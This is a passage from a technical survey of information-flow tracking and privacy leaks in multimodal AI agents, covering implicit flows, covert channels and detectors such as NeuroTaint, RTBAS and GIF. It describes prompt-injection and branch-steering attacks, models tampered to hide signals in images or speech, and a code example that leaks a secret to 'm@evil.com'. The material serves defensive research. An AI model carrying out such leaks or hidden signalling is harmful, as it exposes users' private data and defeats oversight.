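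Rewriting the prompt is also unreliable, because a rewriter usually has to preserve quoted words. When Li and colleagues had GPT-5.4 rewrite openly harmful prompts, the share that safety classifiers flagged fell from 100% to 42.7% on average. For prompts with the harmful content in quoted text, it fell only from 98.3% to 87.5%. If a hospital used a similar step to remove patient details from image prompts, the step would probably miss details inside quotation marks.

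### Copies of retrieved images

In these experiments, the picture was supposed to show something other than the restricted content, but a user can also ask for that content directly. Multimodal retrieval systems search a database for images or recordings related to a query and add them to the model's context, which may then contain a private image that the model could copy.

*Beyond Text* (Zhang, Zeng and colleagues, 2025) tested such systems with requests that asked the model to reproduce whatever it retrieved. From a database of medical images, 500 requests retrieved 101 different images. Depending on the measure of similarity, Gemini 2.0 Flash made close copies of 46 to 81 of them, and the open model Lumina-mGPT made close copies of 41 to 73.

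Gemini leaked content even when converting it to text. With a database of handwriting, it repeated more than 80% of the words on each of the 75 pages the system retrieved. With medical recordings, it repeated more than 80% of the words in 183 of 211 recordings. A filter that compared output images with the database would miss both kinds of leak.

In *Walking the Embedding Space*, Jica, Verberne and colleagues (2026) studied systems that reply with a picture, using public image collections in place of private ones. Their results also depend heavily on what counts as a copy. Across three collections and two models, 23% to 66% of the retrieved images were reproduced with matching local features, but only 3% to 31% were reproduced with most pixels matching. The local-feature measure also falsely matched 10% to 20% of unrelated pairs.

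The requests were designed to obtain copies, so these studies show what the models can pass on, not what they usually pass on. Zhang and colleagues got far fewer copies when they replaced the instruction with a single full stop. This difference matters little for label tracking, because a retrieved scan is in the context whether or not the user asks for a copy, so the picture should carry the scan's label. A search that respects reader lists would also skip any scan the requester is not allowed to see.

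### Facts recovered from stored photos

Some assistants keep text notes and images in long-term memory, and a user may ask them to delete a fact. Kuan Wang and Chao Zhang (2026), in *MEMLEAK*, tested whether the remaining photos can reveal a deleted fact. In one example, a user had deleted a preference for diving in warm tropical waters. The remaining photos, which the system had filed under other facts, included a dive watch, a coral reef and a tropical coastline. A vision-language model inferred the preference from the combination.

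The main experiment used 38 invented people with AI-generated photos. For each of 300 facts, the researchers deleted the text and every image filed under that fact, then asked Claude Sonnet 4 about the fact using only the other images. Three language models judged by majority vote whether the answer revealed the fact. The table compares this test with the other conditions.

| Material available to the model | Deleted facts recovered |
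|---|---|
| Images filed under the deleted fact | 146 of 300 (48.7%) |
| Text about other facts, without images | 55 of 300 (18.3%) |
| Images filed under other facts | 36 of 300 (12.0%) |
| The same images after an extra check of their content | 6 of 300 (2.0%) |
| Images from unrelated people | 1 of 300 (0.3%) |
| Nothing but the question | 0 of 300 (0.0%) |

The last two rows show that the model was not simply guessing. Of the 36 facts recovered from images, 17 could not be recovered from the remaining text. The rate was 9.3% when GPT-4o answered the questions, and 10.6% when stock photographs replaced the generated images. The researchers found these photographs by searching for the text of each fact, so the test shows that the effect also occurs with real photographs, but not how often it would occur with someone's own albums.

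Linking a fact to its images solves part of the problem, because the software can then delete those images along with the text. An extra check asked a vision-language model which of the remaining images hinted at the deleted fact. This cut recovery of the fact from 12.0% to 2.0%, but it also flagged 21% of the remaining images for deletion.

Taint tracking would not have caught the leak in the diving example, because the reef photo was not computed from the text note and no label would have passed from the note to the photo. Joining labels does not help if each photo is harmless on its own. When Cam may see every photo, the joined label also lets Cam see any conclusion drawn from them, even one the user has tried to delete. Whoever labels the photos would have to consider what they reveal together.

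### Voices, background sound and generated code

There is much less evidence about speech output. Zhang and colleagues tested direct copying of sound with only one model, MiniCPM-o 2.6, because their other models read replies aloud in preset voices. They asked it to repeat recordings the system had retrieved. Of 211 medical recordings, it copied 84 according to an AI judge, but 200 or 207 according to two acoustic measures. Of 177 general speech clips, it copied 154 according to the judge, but 90 or 146 according to the acoustic measures.

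The measures disagree so much that the exact rates mean little, but the model clearly could reproduce some of what it had heard. It rarely did so when the request was only a full stop. No one appears to have published a speech version of Braun and colleagues' matched-chat test. Such a version would measure how often a voice, an accent or background sound carries over into an unrelated reply.

*The Model Hears You* (2025) reports that GPT-4o could identify speakers from their voices alone. *Privacy-Preserving End-to-End Full-Duplex Speech Dialogue Models* (2026) examines traces of the speaker's identity in the hidden states of live speech models, but not in the speech they generate.

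Speech recognition can leak less obviously, through text that developers sometimes give a recogniser to help it spell specialised terms. *When Helpful Context Leaks* (2026) reports cases where the recogniser replaced a spoken word with one from this text. If the hospital supplied a list of patients' names, the transcript of the staffing memo could contain a name that nobody said. The transcript therefore needs the join of the memo's label and the list's label.

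A model writing code could copy a password or a patient record from its context into the script. None of the experiments above measured this, so their rates can't be used for the hospital's scheduling script. Software can search a script for an exact copy of a password, which makes it easier to find than a hint in a picture, but a password that the model had split or encoded would be harder to find.

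Research priorities may help explain these gaps. Mireshghallah and Li (2025), in *Position*, reviewed 1,322 papers on AI privacy from 2016 to 2025 and found that 92% were about models memorising their training data or about cryptographic protection for chats. The remaining 8% covered leaks from an agent's context and two other kinds of privacy problem.

### What a tracker has to assume

Even if nobody has tampered with the model, a tracker has to assume that anything in the context may reach the output, because carry-over ranged from almost undetectable on BAGEL to obvious on Emu3.5. A developer could run the matched-chat test on a particular model to estimate how much its labels overstate the risk, but would need to repeat the test for new versions and new kinds of input. Ada can also look at a poster before hanging it up, which helps when carry-over is visible.

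If someone may have tampered with the model, a tracker must treat any output as possibly revealing any fact in the context, however innocent it looks. Braun and colleagues demonstrated this only for images, but they expect the method could extend to audio and video, and that text would have less room to hide a signal. *You Are the Trigger* (2026) describes a different kind of tampering, in which altered speech models suppress or rewrite what a particular person says when they detect that person's voice. A transcript from such a model could depend on who was speaking as well as on the words, so it should keep the recording's label even if the text seems harmless. In those experiments, further training on clean data removed the behaviour.

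Separate contexts still protect against a tampered image generator, because a picture cannot reveal a diagnosis that the generator never received. The model that writes the image prompt needs the same isolation, since a tampered language model could hide a signal in its choice of words.

Checking where a model came from reduces the risk but does not remove it. A hospital can compare a downloaded file's cryptographic hash with the one the developer published. This would expose changes made by someone who redistributed the model, but not a mark the developer had put there.

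## Implicit flows, where content shapes an output without appearing in it

A leak does not require a copied picture or a hidden mark. Suppose the hospital's software uses a two-line program to choose a stock photo for the ward's public web page:

```
photo = "garden.jpg"
if measles_on_ward: photo = "mask.jpg"
```

Both file names are public, and the program never copies anything from a patient's record into `photo`. But a visitor who knows how the program works can tell from the picture whether the ward has measles. This is an implicit flow. A tracker that followed only copying and calculation would label the photo public, because "mask.jpg" is a constant in the code.

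### A label for the program's position

The standard remedy gives a label to the program's current position as well as to its data. This program-counter label, or pc, starts as public. When the program enters a branch, the label of the condition joins the pc:

pc inside the branch = pc before the branch ⊔ ℓ(condition).

Every value that the program assigns inside the branch then gets at least that label:

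ℓ(photo) = ℓ(assigned value) ⊔ pc inside the branch.

If only Ada and Ben may know about the measles, the program assigns "mask.jpg" under the label {Ada, Ben}. The variable `photo` gets that reader list, so the software keeps the picture off the public page. When the branch ends, the pc returns to its earlier value.

The pc also applies to actions. In an example from Garby and colleagues, an injected instruction would leak information about a customer's bank balance by sending the email "rich!" only if the balance exceeds a threshold. The email's text is a constant, but CaMeL blocks the email because the pc carries the balance's label when the program reaches the email tool.

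### The branch not taken

This rule fails when the ward has no measles. The program then skips its second line, so nothing raises the label of `photo`, which stays public and keeps the value "garden.jpg". A visitor who sees the garden learns that there is no measles.

A second variable can make the program reveal the other answer too. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter is open to this trick, which they trace to Fenton's work in 1974 and Denning's 1976 paper. In their example, the program prepares a public flag called `rich`:

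```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `if balance > threshold` | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
| `if tmp` | Skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
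| `if rich` | The email goes out | No email goes out |

In both runs, `rich` ends up public and equal to the secret, so the interpreter treats the last condition as harmless and allows the email. A purely dynamic tracker examines only the lines that run, so it cannot label an assignment that never happens.

A compiler can track implicit flows by inspecting the program in advance and raising the label of every variable that either branch might change. This is difficult when a model writes more code during a run. LLMbda instead stops any program that tries to change public state inside a branch that depends on a secret. In one of Garby and colleagues' tests, a program tells a model that x is false, sends "Set x = true" only if a secret is true, and then asks the model for x. The interpreter stops at the conditional message because sending it would make a public conversation depend on the secret.

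Multi-CaMeL extends CaMeL's interpreter, and Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that it misses the same implicit flows. The current software could therefore let an instruction to another agent depend implicitly on a tool result.

### One bit per run

Anyone who sees the program stop still learns that the secret was true. Garby and colleagues note that most information-flow systems let such failures leak at least one bit per run. Preventing this leak would mean rejecting every program whose completion might depend on a secret, including many useful ones.

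The tolerance is reasonable only if an attacker cannot trigger many runs. A program that leaks by stopping can reveal only one bit per run, whereas one that exploits the untaken branch can leak repeatedly within a run. A retry loop outside the tracker, like the one around CaMeL, also removes the one-bit limit. Suppose an attacker can ask one yes-or-no question per run about a patient's date of birth, such as whether it falls before 1970. A century contains about 36,500 dates, and each answer can halve the remaining range, so sixteen runs are enough to find the date (2¹⁶ = 65,536).

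Multi-CaMeL does not retry failed runs, so it avoids this leak. A user who kept resubmitting a failed request would recreate the retry loop manually.

### Choices inside a model

Software cannot see branches inside a model, so it cannot attach a program-counter (pc) label to them. The smallest step it can label from outside is the whole model call. Conservative merge treats that call as one large branch on everything in the context, so it covers implicit flows without having to find them. Any method that assigns narrower labels has to account for restricted content that influences the model's choices without appearing in the output.

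In a variant of the stock photo example, a language model picks the photo of the masked nurse because the voice memo mentions measles. Every pixel comes from the photo agency, so a filter that compared the picture with the memo would find no match, and signed provenance metadata would correctly name the agency as the source. The photo file can stay public, but the web page should carry the memo's label because the page reveals which photo the model chose.

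Speech can reveal a secret even if its words do not. A model might read "Visiting ends at eight" in a subdued voice because its context mentions a death on the ward. The transcript would be the same on any other day, so checking it would not reveal the leak. In a modular pipeline, a speech synthesiser that receives only the approved sentence has no information about the death. If the language model also sends a style setting, such as "calm" or "sombre", that setting must carry the label of the model's context. A unified model has no separate setting to inspect, so the software must apply that label to the whole recording.

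If an assistant refuses to make posters for psoriasis patients but makes them for everyone else, each refusal reveals a diagnosis. A tracker that labels only finished files would miss this leak, because a refusal has no content to inspect. Refusals and error messages therefore need labels too, including a message that the label check has blocked a poster. LLMbda, for example, labels the result of every label test.

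Sensitive content can influence a default value in generated code. For example, the scheduling script might contain `max_visitors = 1` because the whiteboard shows a patient in isolation. A search for names or copied phrases would not find this flow, since the number 1 appears in most scripts. The model chose the constant before the script ran, so even a system like Elba would have to give the script the label of the model's context from the start.

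### How much a choice can carry

The limit of log₂ n bits for a choice among n values applies to visual choices too, so a model that picks one of 16 backgrounds can reveal up to log₂ 16 = 4 bits per image. Twelve images allow 16¹² combinations, so together they can reveal up to

12 × 4 = 48 bits.

That is enough to encode any 14-digit number, since 2⁴⁸ is about 281 trillion. A ten-digit patient number would fit in nine images.

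To reach these maximums, the model would have to use every background equally often, choose each one independently, and follow a code that the observer knows. The total also cannot exceed the observer's uncertainty about the secret S. If Y₁ to Y₁₂ are the backgrounds, then

I(S; Y₁, …, Y₁₂) ≤ min(H(S), 48 bits).

If all 12 backgrounds depend only on which of four equally likely diagnoses a patient has, the images reveal at most 2 bits in total. The full 48 bits matter more when the context holds many secrets, or when someone has altered the model to send a message.

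The calculation covers only the choice of background. A model that also varies the layout or lighting can reveal more. Ordinary software can keep the background from revealing anything by choosing it at random or by a rule that ignores the restricted context.

### Covert channels

Butler Lampson introduced the term covert channel in 1973 for a route that nobody designed to carry information, such as a program's effect on how busy a computer is. *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* (2026) restates the problem he was studying, in which a customer has to share confidential data with a service program and wants a guarantee that none of it will reach the program's owner.

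The term implicit flow describes how a secret influences a result, while covert channel describes a route by which information escapes. The choice of stock photo is an implicit flow through the web page, an ordinary output that software can label. Even the invisible marks that Braun and colleagues put in pictures travel through an ordinary output. But if the assistant takes longer to make a poster when a patient has a long medical history, the delay is a covert channel, and labeling the poster does not hide it.

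If a program does extra work only when the ward has measles, it has an implicit flow, and its response time can reveal whether measles is present. LLMbda's theorems would not rule out this leak, because they compare what a program returns and how likely it is to finish, not how long it takes.

Lampson suspected that designers could not guarantee that even a moderately complicated system has no covert channels. Where they cannot remove a channel, he advised reducing its capacity as far as they can while keeping the system useful. An observer who can distinguish eight response times could learn up to 3 bits from each response. The hospital could release every poster exactly one minute after the request, which would hide the differences in timing unless a poster took longer than a minute to make. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that finding channels and reducing their capacity may not be enough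 when agents act strategically.

### NeuroTaint's counterfactual test

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen, Tang and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, which searches the logs of text-based agents for implicit flows. It links untrusted sources, such as web searches, to sinks, such as sending email or running code. It can also follow content that an agent stores in memory and uses in a later session.

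For each sink call, NeuroTaint first checks the call's arguments for the source's content, looking for planted markers, overlapping text and similar meaning. If it finds none, it assesses whether the agent would have made the same call had the source contained something neutral, such as "No relevant information found". By Cai and colleagues' definition, the source implicitly influenced the call if replacing the source's content would prevent the call or change its arguments.

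In one example, a poisoned search result tells an agent to submit its findings to an outside address before running any code. The agent then calls an upload tool instead of the code runner. Without the search result, it would have had no reason to upload anything. The flow is not purely implicit, because the attacker's address appears in both the search result and the call.

NeuroTaint gives a language model the original history and the altered one, then asks whether the agent would still make the call, without rerunning the agent. The answer is a prediction, and its confidence score is the judging model's own estimate. The hospital could test more directly whether the memo influenced its stock photos by replacing the memo with a neutral one, generating the page several times and comparing the photos chosen.

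The test can miss some influences. It replaces one source at a time, so if two web pages each give the agent enough reason to send an email, replacing either page alone would not stop the email. It also runs only when the agent makes a sink call, so it would miss a source that caused the agent to refuse.

NeuroTaint audits the log after the run, so it does not slow the agent down, but it also cannot stop the agent from sending an email.

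### Results on TaintBench

Cai and colleagues built and labelled their own benchmark, TaintBench, to evaluate NeuroTaint. It contains 400 scenarios, 20 for each of 20 agent frameworks. In half of the scenarios, the source's content is supposed to reach or influence the sink. They used GPT-4.1 mini as the agent, ran each scenario five times, and counted a detection when at least three of the five runs raised an alarm.

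The table compares NeuroTaint with a version of FIDES used as a detector. The F1 score combines precision, the share of alarms that are correct, with recall, the share of real flows that a system finds.

| Measure | NeuroTaint | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| Overall F1 | 0.928 | 0.522 |
| All flows found | 187 of 200 | 108 of 200 |
| Implicit-control flows found | 37 of 40 | 17 of 40 |
| False alarms | 16 of 200 | 106 of 200 |
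| False alarms when only the topic overlapped | 14 of 14 | 9 of 14 |

NeuroTaint raised false alarms in all 14 scenarios where the output shared a topic with the source but did not depend on it. In the hospital, a similar tracker might flag a routine hand-washing poster because the memo mentioned an infection.

The gap between the two systems is hard to interpret. The FIDES detector raised no alarms on four of the frameworks, so it may not have worked properly with them. Excluding those four would raise its F1 only to about 0.58. But the detector also missed 23 of the 40 implicit-control flows, even though the context label in Costa and colleagues' design covers every call an agent plans after reading untrusted content. On InjecAgent, an existing benchmark that scores unsafe actions instead of flows, the two systems had nearly equal F1 scores of 0.994 and 0.993 in the basic setting.

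Cai and colleagues finalised TaintBench's labels before comparing the systems, which makes it less likely that they adjusted the labels to favour NeuroTaint. NeuroTaint's usual threshold for similar meaning was 0.60, but "safe-control policies" used a stricter 0.95. If that phrase refers to the harmless scenarios, the stricter threshold would have reduced false alarms in a way that a deployed tracker could not, because the tracker would not know in advance which runs were harmless.

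NeuroTaint's F1 fell to 0.678 when Claude Opus 4.6 was the agent. Stronger models sometimes blocked an attack before it reached the sink, but the scoring still counted the scenario as a flow that NeuroTaint should detect. The lower score therefore reflects both blocked attacks and missed flows.

All these results are for text and tool calls. Cai and colleagues excluded multimodal attacks, such as image patches designed to mislead a model, and did not test whether NeuroTaint could detect a flow through a choice of photo or a tone of voice.

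### Branch steering

Untrusted content can also determine what an agent does without appearing in the action. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* introduced the term "branch steering" for attacks that use this influence to make an agent follow a harmful path in its own plan. For example, a plan might include a routine for closing cookie banners. An attacker can disguise an advertisement as a cookie banner, so that the vision model returns the advertisement's coordinates. The agent then clicks the advertisement and arrives at the attacker's website, even though every step was in the plan.

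The same thing can happen in multi-CaMeL without a screen. A parent agent's plan might send a child agent one instruction if a tool returns a certain value and another if it does not. Anyone who controls the tool's result can then choose which instruction the child receives.

Peters-Gill and colleagues accept branch steering because they want to guarantee control-flow integrity, meaning that agents follow only plans based on the user's request and other trusted information. An attacker can influence which of the plan's two instructions the agents follow but cannot add a third. The researchers acknowledge that branch steering would violate noninterference, which forbids untrusted data from changing the agents' visible actions in this way.

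Accepting some steering is practical because agents could not do data-dependent tasks without it. But the number of bits is a poor measure of the potential harm, since a single bit can determine whether an agent makes a payment.

*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) tests how well existing agents resist steering. Its benchmark, STEER-Bench, has 101 tasks in areas such as bank transfers, warehouse logistics and changes to medication doses. The researchers could run 74 of its attack configurations on existing agents that read the screen. The attacks succeeded 90.5% of the time against an agent that chose each action after looking at the screen, and 87.8% of the time against CaMeL for computer use. Planning in advance, as CaMeL does, offered little protection against attacks that stayed within the plan.

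Their own system, COBRA, sets limits for each branch before the agent sees any untrusted content. The limits specify which websites and tools the branch may use and, when the necessary information is available, which values it may send. If the user's permission depends on a fact that only untrusted content could establish, the planner asks the user about it before the run begins.

COBRA enforces these limits on outgoing web requests and tool calls, because the same click might open a preview on one page and submit a payment on another. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* had argued that this ambiguity would make any defence against such attacks on computer-use agents probabilistic. COBRA can apply a fixed rule instead because it checks the request that a click produces.

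COBRA blocked every attack on STEER-Bench and retained 97% of the agent's performance on tasks without attacks. Zingrillo and colleagues designed both the defence and the benchmark, but COBRA also blocked 1,289 of 1,312 attack cases from four other published benchmarks. COBRA does not check whether a branch's condition is true, so an attacker may still be able to choose the branch. The protection depends on whether the limits on that branch match what the user authorised.

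Limits of this kind protect integrity but do not hide which branch the agent took. Even if the hospital's web-page assistant could only switch between the garden photo and the mask photo, visitors could still tell from the photo whether the ward had measles.

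## Measuring the influence of an input on an output

Conservative merge covers a model's internal choices but often produces labels that are too strict. Several groups have tried to relax these labels by estimating which inputs influenced the output. Any estimate can be wrong, so safety depends on whether the system generates the output again without the inputs that seemed unimportant, or keeps the original output and only drops those inputs' labels.

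### Permissive propagation

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, drop the labels of documents that a model could have done without. Their method, which they tested on text, has four steps:

1. The model answers from the full context.
2. Software looks for a more permissive label whose documents would have made that answer almost as likely.
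3. The model answers again from those documents alone.
4. The system returns the second answer with the new label and discards the first.

Let x be the prompt, y the first answer and C the full context. For a candidate label L′, let C′ be the documents in C whose labels may flow to L′. The label qualifies if

PPL(y | x, C′) − PPL(y | x, C) ≤ λ.

PPL is perplexity, which is 1 divided by the geometric mean of the probabilities the model gives to the answer's tokens. The developer chooses the tolerance λ.

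Suppose the hospital assistant answers a question about visiting hours from a public notice and the restricted memo, and gives every token of its answer a probability of 0.8. The perplexity is 1/0.8 = 1.25. If each probability falls to 0.75 without the memo, the perplexity rises by 0.08, to 1.33. Because this rise is less than λ = 0.2, the assistant may answer again from the notice alone and label the result public. If each probability falls to 0.5, the perplexity rises by 0.75 and the memo's label stays.

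The software searches through labels rather than every subset of documents. With only two labels, public and restricted, it has one alternative to test. If every document has its own label, the number of model calls can grow exponentially with the number of documents.

Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method with two sizes of Llama-2, a 2023 model family. In the hardest search, each question came with 14 invented personal records, each with its own label, so there were 2¹⁴ = 16,384 possible combinations. The method found exactly the right combinations for 85.9% of questions with either model. When the researchers instead asked the models which documents mattered, the smaller one was right 1.6% of the time and the larger one 12.7%.

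The results were weaker on news articles. Siddiqui and colleagues paired trusted articles with untrusted ones on similar topics and used GPT-4 to write 3,465 questions, of which 647 did not need the untrusted article. The smaller model correctly relaxed the label for 56.7% of these 647 questions, and the larger one for 39.3%. Of the labels the smaller model relaxed, 22.7% should have stayed unchanged because the answer needed the untrusted article, compared with 18.6% for the larger model. The researchers attribute the weaker results to the lower quality of the automatically written questions.

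A third test used 40 conversations in which an assistant searched the web, email or a calendar. The label could safely improve in 20 of them, and the method improved it in 17 with the smaller model and 19 with the larger one.

### When dropping a label is safe

A wrong estimate in step 2 can make the second answer worse, but it cannot put text from an excluded document into that answer, because the model no longer has the document. This holds even if the document contains a prompt injection. The system loses this protection if it releases the first answer under the new label to save a model call.

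The choice of label can still leak restricted information, because the software chooses the label after processing the full context. Suppose a public notice says the ward is open to visitors on Friday, and the hospital automatically publishes any answer labelled public. If the restricted memo matches the notice, the answer doesn't need the memo, so it is labelled public and published. If the memo says that measles has closed the ward, the answer from the full context is "no", which would be unlikely from the notice alone, so the label stays restricted and nothing is published. A visitor who knows the rule can infer from the missing answer that the memo contradicts the notice. With two possible labels, this reveals at most one bit per answer.

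An older technique called secure multi-execution avoids this leak by running a program separately for each level of clearance. The public run gets dummy values in place of secrets, and the public always sees the output of that run. In the example, visitors would always get the answer based on the notice, which would be wrong when the memo announced a closure.

Siddiqui and colleagues point out that if a developer knows in advance who will see an output, the system does not need to search for a label, because it can give the model only documents with suitable labels. The hospital's corridor poster is such a case. Searching is more useful when the audience may grow later, as when people forward an email. Costa and colleagues note that FIDES could support this kind of propagation, though they left it out to keep their system simple.

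### Screening before each tool call

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen et al., 2025) applies a similar idea to agents that use tools. Before the agent's next step, a screener marks the regions of the conversation that seem relevant. The software joins their labels and masks every region whose label is not allowed to flow to the joined label. The agent then plans its next tool call from what remains. If the joined label breaks the tool's policy, the system asks the user to confirm the call.

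If the hospital's screener marked only the voice memo as relevant, the joined label would be {Ada, Ben, Cam}. The software would mask the whiteboard photo, which Cam may not see, but leave the style guide visible because it is public.

Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One uses a language model to identify which regions the next step needs. The other runs a small open model over the conversation and a draft of the agent's output. It weights the model's attention by how strongly that attention affects the prediction of each output token, then passes summary statistics for each region to a small trained network. The network was 81% accurate on test data.

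On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as the agent, RTBAS stopped every attack that broke its policies. It could not stop an injection in text the user had written, because that text had a trusted label. Without attacks, task completion fell by 10% with the model screener and 7.4% with the attention screener. On the Slack tasks it fell to 22% and 33% respectively, since many of them involve acting on untrusted websites. The tests skipped blocked calls instead of asking a user, so some of these tasks could have succeeded with approval. The attention screener was also trained on 40 AgentDojo cases, so its scores may be too favourable.

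Zhong and colleagues wrote 37 further cases to test privacy in payment, flight-booking and shopping apps. The table shows how often each approach made a mistake about asking the user.

| Approach | Asked unnecessarily | Masked private data when it should have asked |
|---|---|---|
| Ask before every call | 11 of 37 | 0 of 37 |
| Mask all private data and never ask | 0 of 37 | 19 of 37 |
| RTBAS, model screener | 3 of 37 | 4 of 37 |
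| RTBAS, attention screener | 6 of 37 | 4 of 37 |

The mistakes in the last column leave the agent without data the task needed, such as a card number for a booking, but they do not expose private data.

With the model screener, about 70% of tool calls got exactly the right set of private-data labels, compared with 57.3% with the attention screener. Conservative merge, which assumes that every call used all the private data in the context, got 56.7% right, so the attention screener barely improved on it by this measure. Both screeners roughly doubled the time per banking task, from 4.4 seconds to 8.7 with the attention screener and 9.7 with the model screener.

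RTBAS needs one screening step, whereas permissive propagation may need many model calls. The agent plans from the masked conversation, so a screening mistake cannot reveal the contents of a masked region. But the screener reads everything before deciding what to mask, so its choice of what to mask can leak information, just as the choice of label can in the measles example.

### Geometric Information Flow

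A screener decides only whether an input matters. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposed softer labels that would record how much information an output carries about each input. *GIF*, published in June 2026, provides such a measure for text models, called Geometric Information Flow.

The method adds a small random disturbance U, with variance τ in each coordinate, to the token embeddings of one span of the prompt, such as a sentence of a CV. It leaves the rest of the prompt unchanged. If the disturbance noticeably changes the probabilities of the next token Y, then Y carries information about U. The mutual information I(U; Y) measures how much, in bits.

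Computing I(U; Y) exactly would require averaging the model's predictions over every possible disturbance. For small disturbances, however, the model behaves almost linearly, so the researchers replace it with a simpler channel that adds Gaussian noise N:

Z = AU + N, where A = F^½ W J.

The matrix J describes how a small change to the span moves the model's final hidden state, and W turns that movement into changes in the tokens' scores. The matrix F = diag(p) − ppᵀ accounts for how much those changes affect the current token probabilities p.

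The two channels match for small disturbances. If u is one particular disturbance, the Kullback–Leibler divergence, a standard measure of how far one distribution is from another, is about ½uᵀAᵀAu for the model's next-token distribution. For the Gaussian channel it is exactly that. The information that passes through the Gaussian channel has a simple formula:

GIF = ½ log₂ det(I + τAAᵀ) = ½ Σ log₂(1 + τλᵢ).

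The λᵢ are the eigenvalues of AAᵀ, which measure how visibly the output responds to disturbances in different directions. For τ = 1 and eigenvalues 3 and 0,

GIF = ½ log₂((1 + 3)(1 + 0)) = ½ log₂ 4 = 1 bit.

All of this comes from the first direction. To a first approximation, a disturbance in the second direction has no effect on the next token.

Even this formula requires a lot of computation, because building J takes one backward pass through the model for each of its thousands of hidden dimensions. The researchers therefore estimate the sum of the eigenvalues from a few random probes. Half this sum, multiplied by τ, is an upper limit on GIF in natural units. In the example, the limit is 1.5, or about 2.16 bits, which is more than twice the true value. At τ = 0.01, the limit and the true value are both about 0.02 bits.

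With only a few probes, the estimates are better for ranking tokens than for counting bits. On 150 tokens from AgentDojo tool calls, 8 probes reproduced the exact ranking almost perfectly, with a correlation of 0.986, but the scores had a relative error of about 41%. The proven error bounds require about 181 probes to get within 10% of the true sum with 95% probability.

### The hiring example

In *GIF*'s main example, an agent screens job applicants. Its trusted instructions require at least five years of professional experience in Python and machine learning. One applicant has two years of JavaScript and some Python, but the agent follows an instruction hidden in the CV to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000.

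The researchers estimate that 82 bits flow into the recommendation from the injected instruction, 27 from the system prompt and 16 from the rest of the context. The employer using the agent could take this as a warning that the applicant had more influence on the decision than the hiring criteria did.

But a large flow is not always a violation. A strong applicant's work history should influence the decision, even though it comes from the same untrusted CV, so someone still has to decide which kinds of influence are acceptable.

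### Results on agent benchmarks

The researchers tested the measure on text records of six open-weight models acting as agents on three benchmarks. AgentDojo and MSB, which covers tools connected through MCP, test for prompt injection, and AgentDAM tests for privacy leaks in web tasks. For each tool call or action, the software ranked the input tokens by influence. It then used the benchmark's annotations to calculate what share of the top tokens belonged to an injection or to private data.

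The table shows the AUC, the probability that a run with a violation scored higher than one without. Each range runs from the result for the top 5 tokens to the result for the top 50, averaged over the six models.

| Benchmark | GIF | Simpler gradient score | RTBAS attention |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, integrity | 0.75–0.91 | 0.73–0.90 | 0.56–0.84 |
| MSB, integrity | 0.84–0.92 | 0.84–0.92 | 0.53–0.76 |
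| AgentDAM, confidentiality | 0.64–0.75 | 0.61–0.74 | 0.54–0.57 |

The simpler score uses only the token the model produced, not the whole distribution. It did almost as well as GIF, so most of the improvement over attention seems to come from using gradients, not from the information-theoretic formula. The ranking was different on ordinary program calls, where Xu and colleagues later found that RTBAS identified the inputs that reached the output more accurately than GIF did.

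*GIF*'s abstract describes recall as near-perfect even without a further check, but the paper reports AUC and precision–recall scores for this test, not recall rates. With an AUC of 0.75 on AgentDAM, catching nearly every leak would probably cause many false alarms. The test also relies on annotations of injections and private data that a deployed system would not have.

The researchers also asked GPT-5.5 to pick out the most influential tokens in a sample of runs. Its AUC ranged from 0.73 to 0.87, compared with 0.80 to 0.91 for GIF, and it cost an average of $147.90 per agent model, compared with GIF's $15.98.

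GIF can also shorten the evidence that a judging model reads when deciding whether to allow an action. With only the one to three most influential spans, judges' scores were 0.97 to 1.22 times their scores with the full record. On AgentDojo and MSB, showing one span used 27% to 37% as many tokens as showing the full record. AgentDAM records were already short, so the reduction there was only about a fifth to a quarter.

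GIF needs gradients, which many commercial models do not expose to outsiders. The researchers therefore used a small open model, Qwen3 0.6B, to analyse AgentDojo runs by Qwen3 32B and GPT-OSS 120B. A judge then used the selected spans to detect violations. Using the small model in place of the agent's own model changed the judge's F1 score by at most 0.7 percentage points, even though GPT-OSS 120B is 200 times larger than Qwen3 0.6B.

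This works for ordinary dependencies that both models are likely to share. It would be much less reliable for a tampered model like those in Braun and colleagues' experiments. A clean surrogate has not learned to put a hidden mark in a picture when a user mentions depression, so it would not be expected to show that dependency.

### What "locally sound" means

*GIF*'s main theorem states that, if the model is smooth enough around the given prompt,

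I(U; Y) ≤ GIF + o(τ) as τ → 0.

The term o(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ. So for small enough disturbances to one span of one prompt, the formula underestimates the flow to the next token by at most this error. The proof first compares the disturbed predictions with the original prediction instead of with their own average. This change can only increase the measured flow. The proof then averages over the disturbances and shows that the result matches the Gaussian formula in the limit. The proof checker Lean has verified the theorem.

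The theorem does not cover a change from "asthma" to "eczema", because that is a large jump in the embedding. As with the poster's palette, a confident model may barely respond to small disturbances but change its output completely when given a different word. In one of *GIF*'s examples, an agent turned private notes into a public comment that left out a street address, and the address scored zero. That score alone does not prove that a different address would have produced the same comment.

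GIF also measures information about the artificial disturbance rather than about the secret. In the earlier example, knowing which of the four equally likely diagnoses a patient has provides 2 bits, but the word "asthma" could score more than 2 because the disturbance can take infinitely many values. Limiting GIF to k bits therefore does not limit what a poster reveals about a patient to k bits.

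For these reasons, a system should not drop an input's label and release the original output because the input's GIF score is low. It could instead use GIF as the screener, remove the inputs with low scores and generate the output again without them. A wrong score would then have the same limited consequences as a wrong estimate in permissive propagation.

### Outputs made of image or audio tokens

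*GIF* reports experiments only on text, so we can only infer from its formula that it would work for pictures and speech. The formula needs input vectors that software can perturb and a probability distribution over the output. Some image generators provide both. For example, *OmniGen-AR* (2026) converts text and reference pictures into tokens and uses one transformer to generate new image tokens. A developer could perturb the embeddings of the whiteboard photo and measure the effect on each token of the poster. The same calculation should work for a speech model that predicts audio tokens.

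The measurement would have to cover the whole picture or recording. For n output tokens, the total information is

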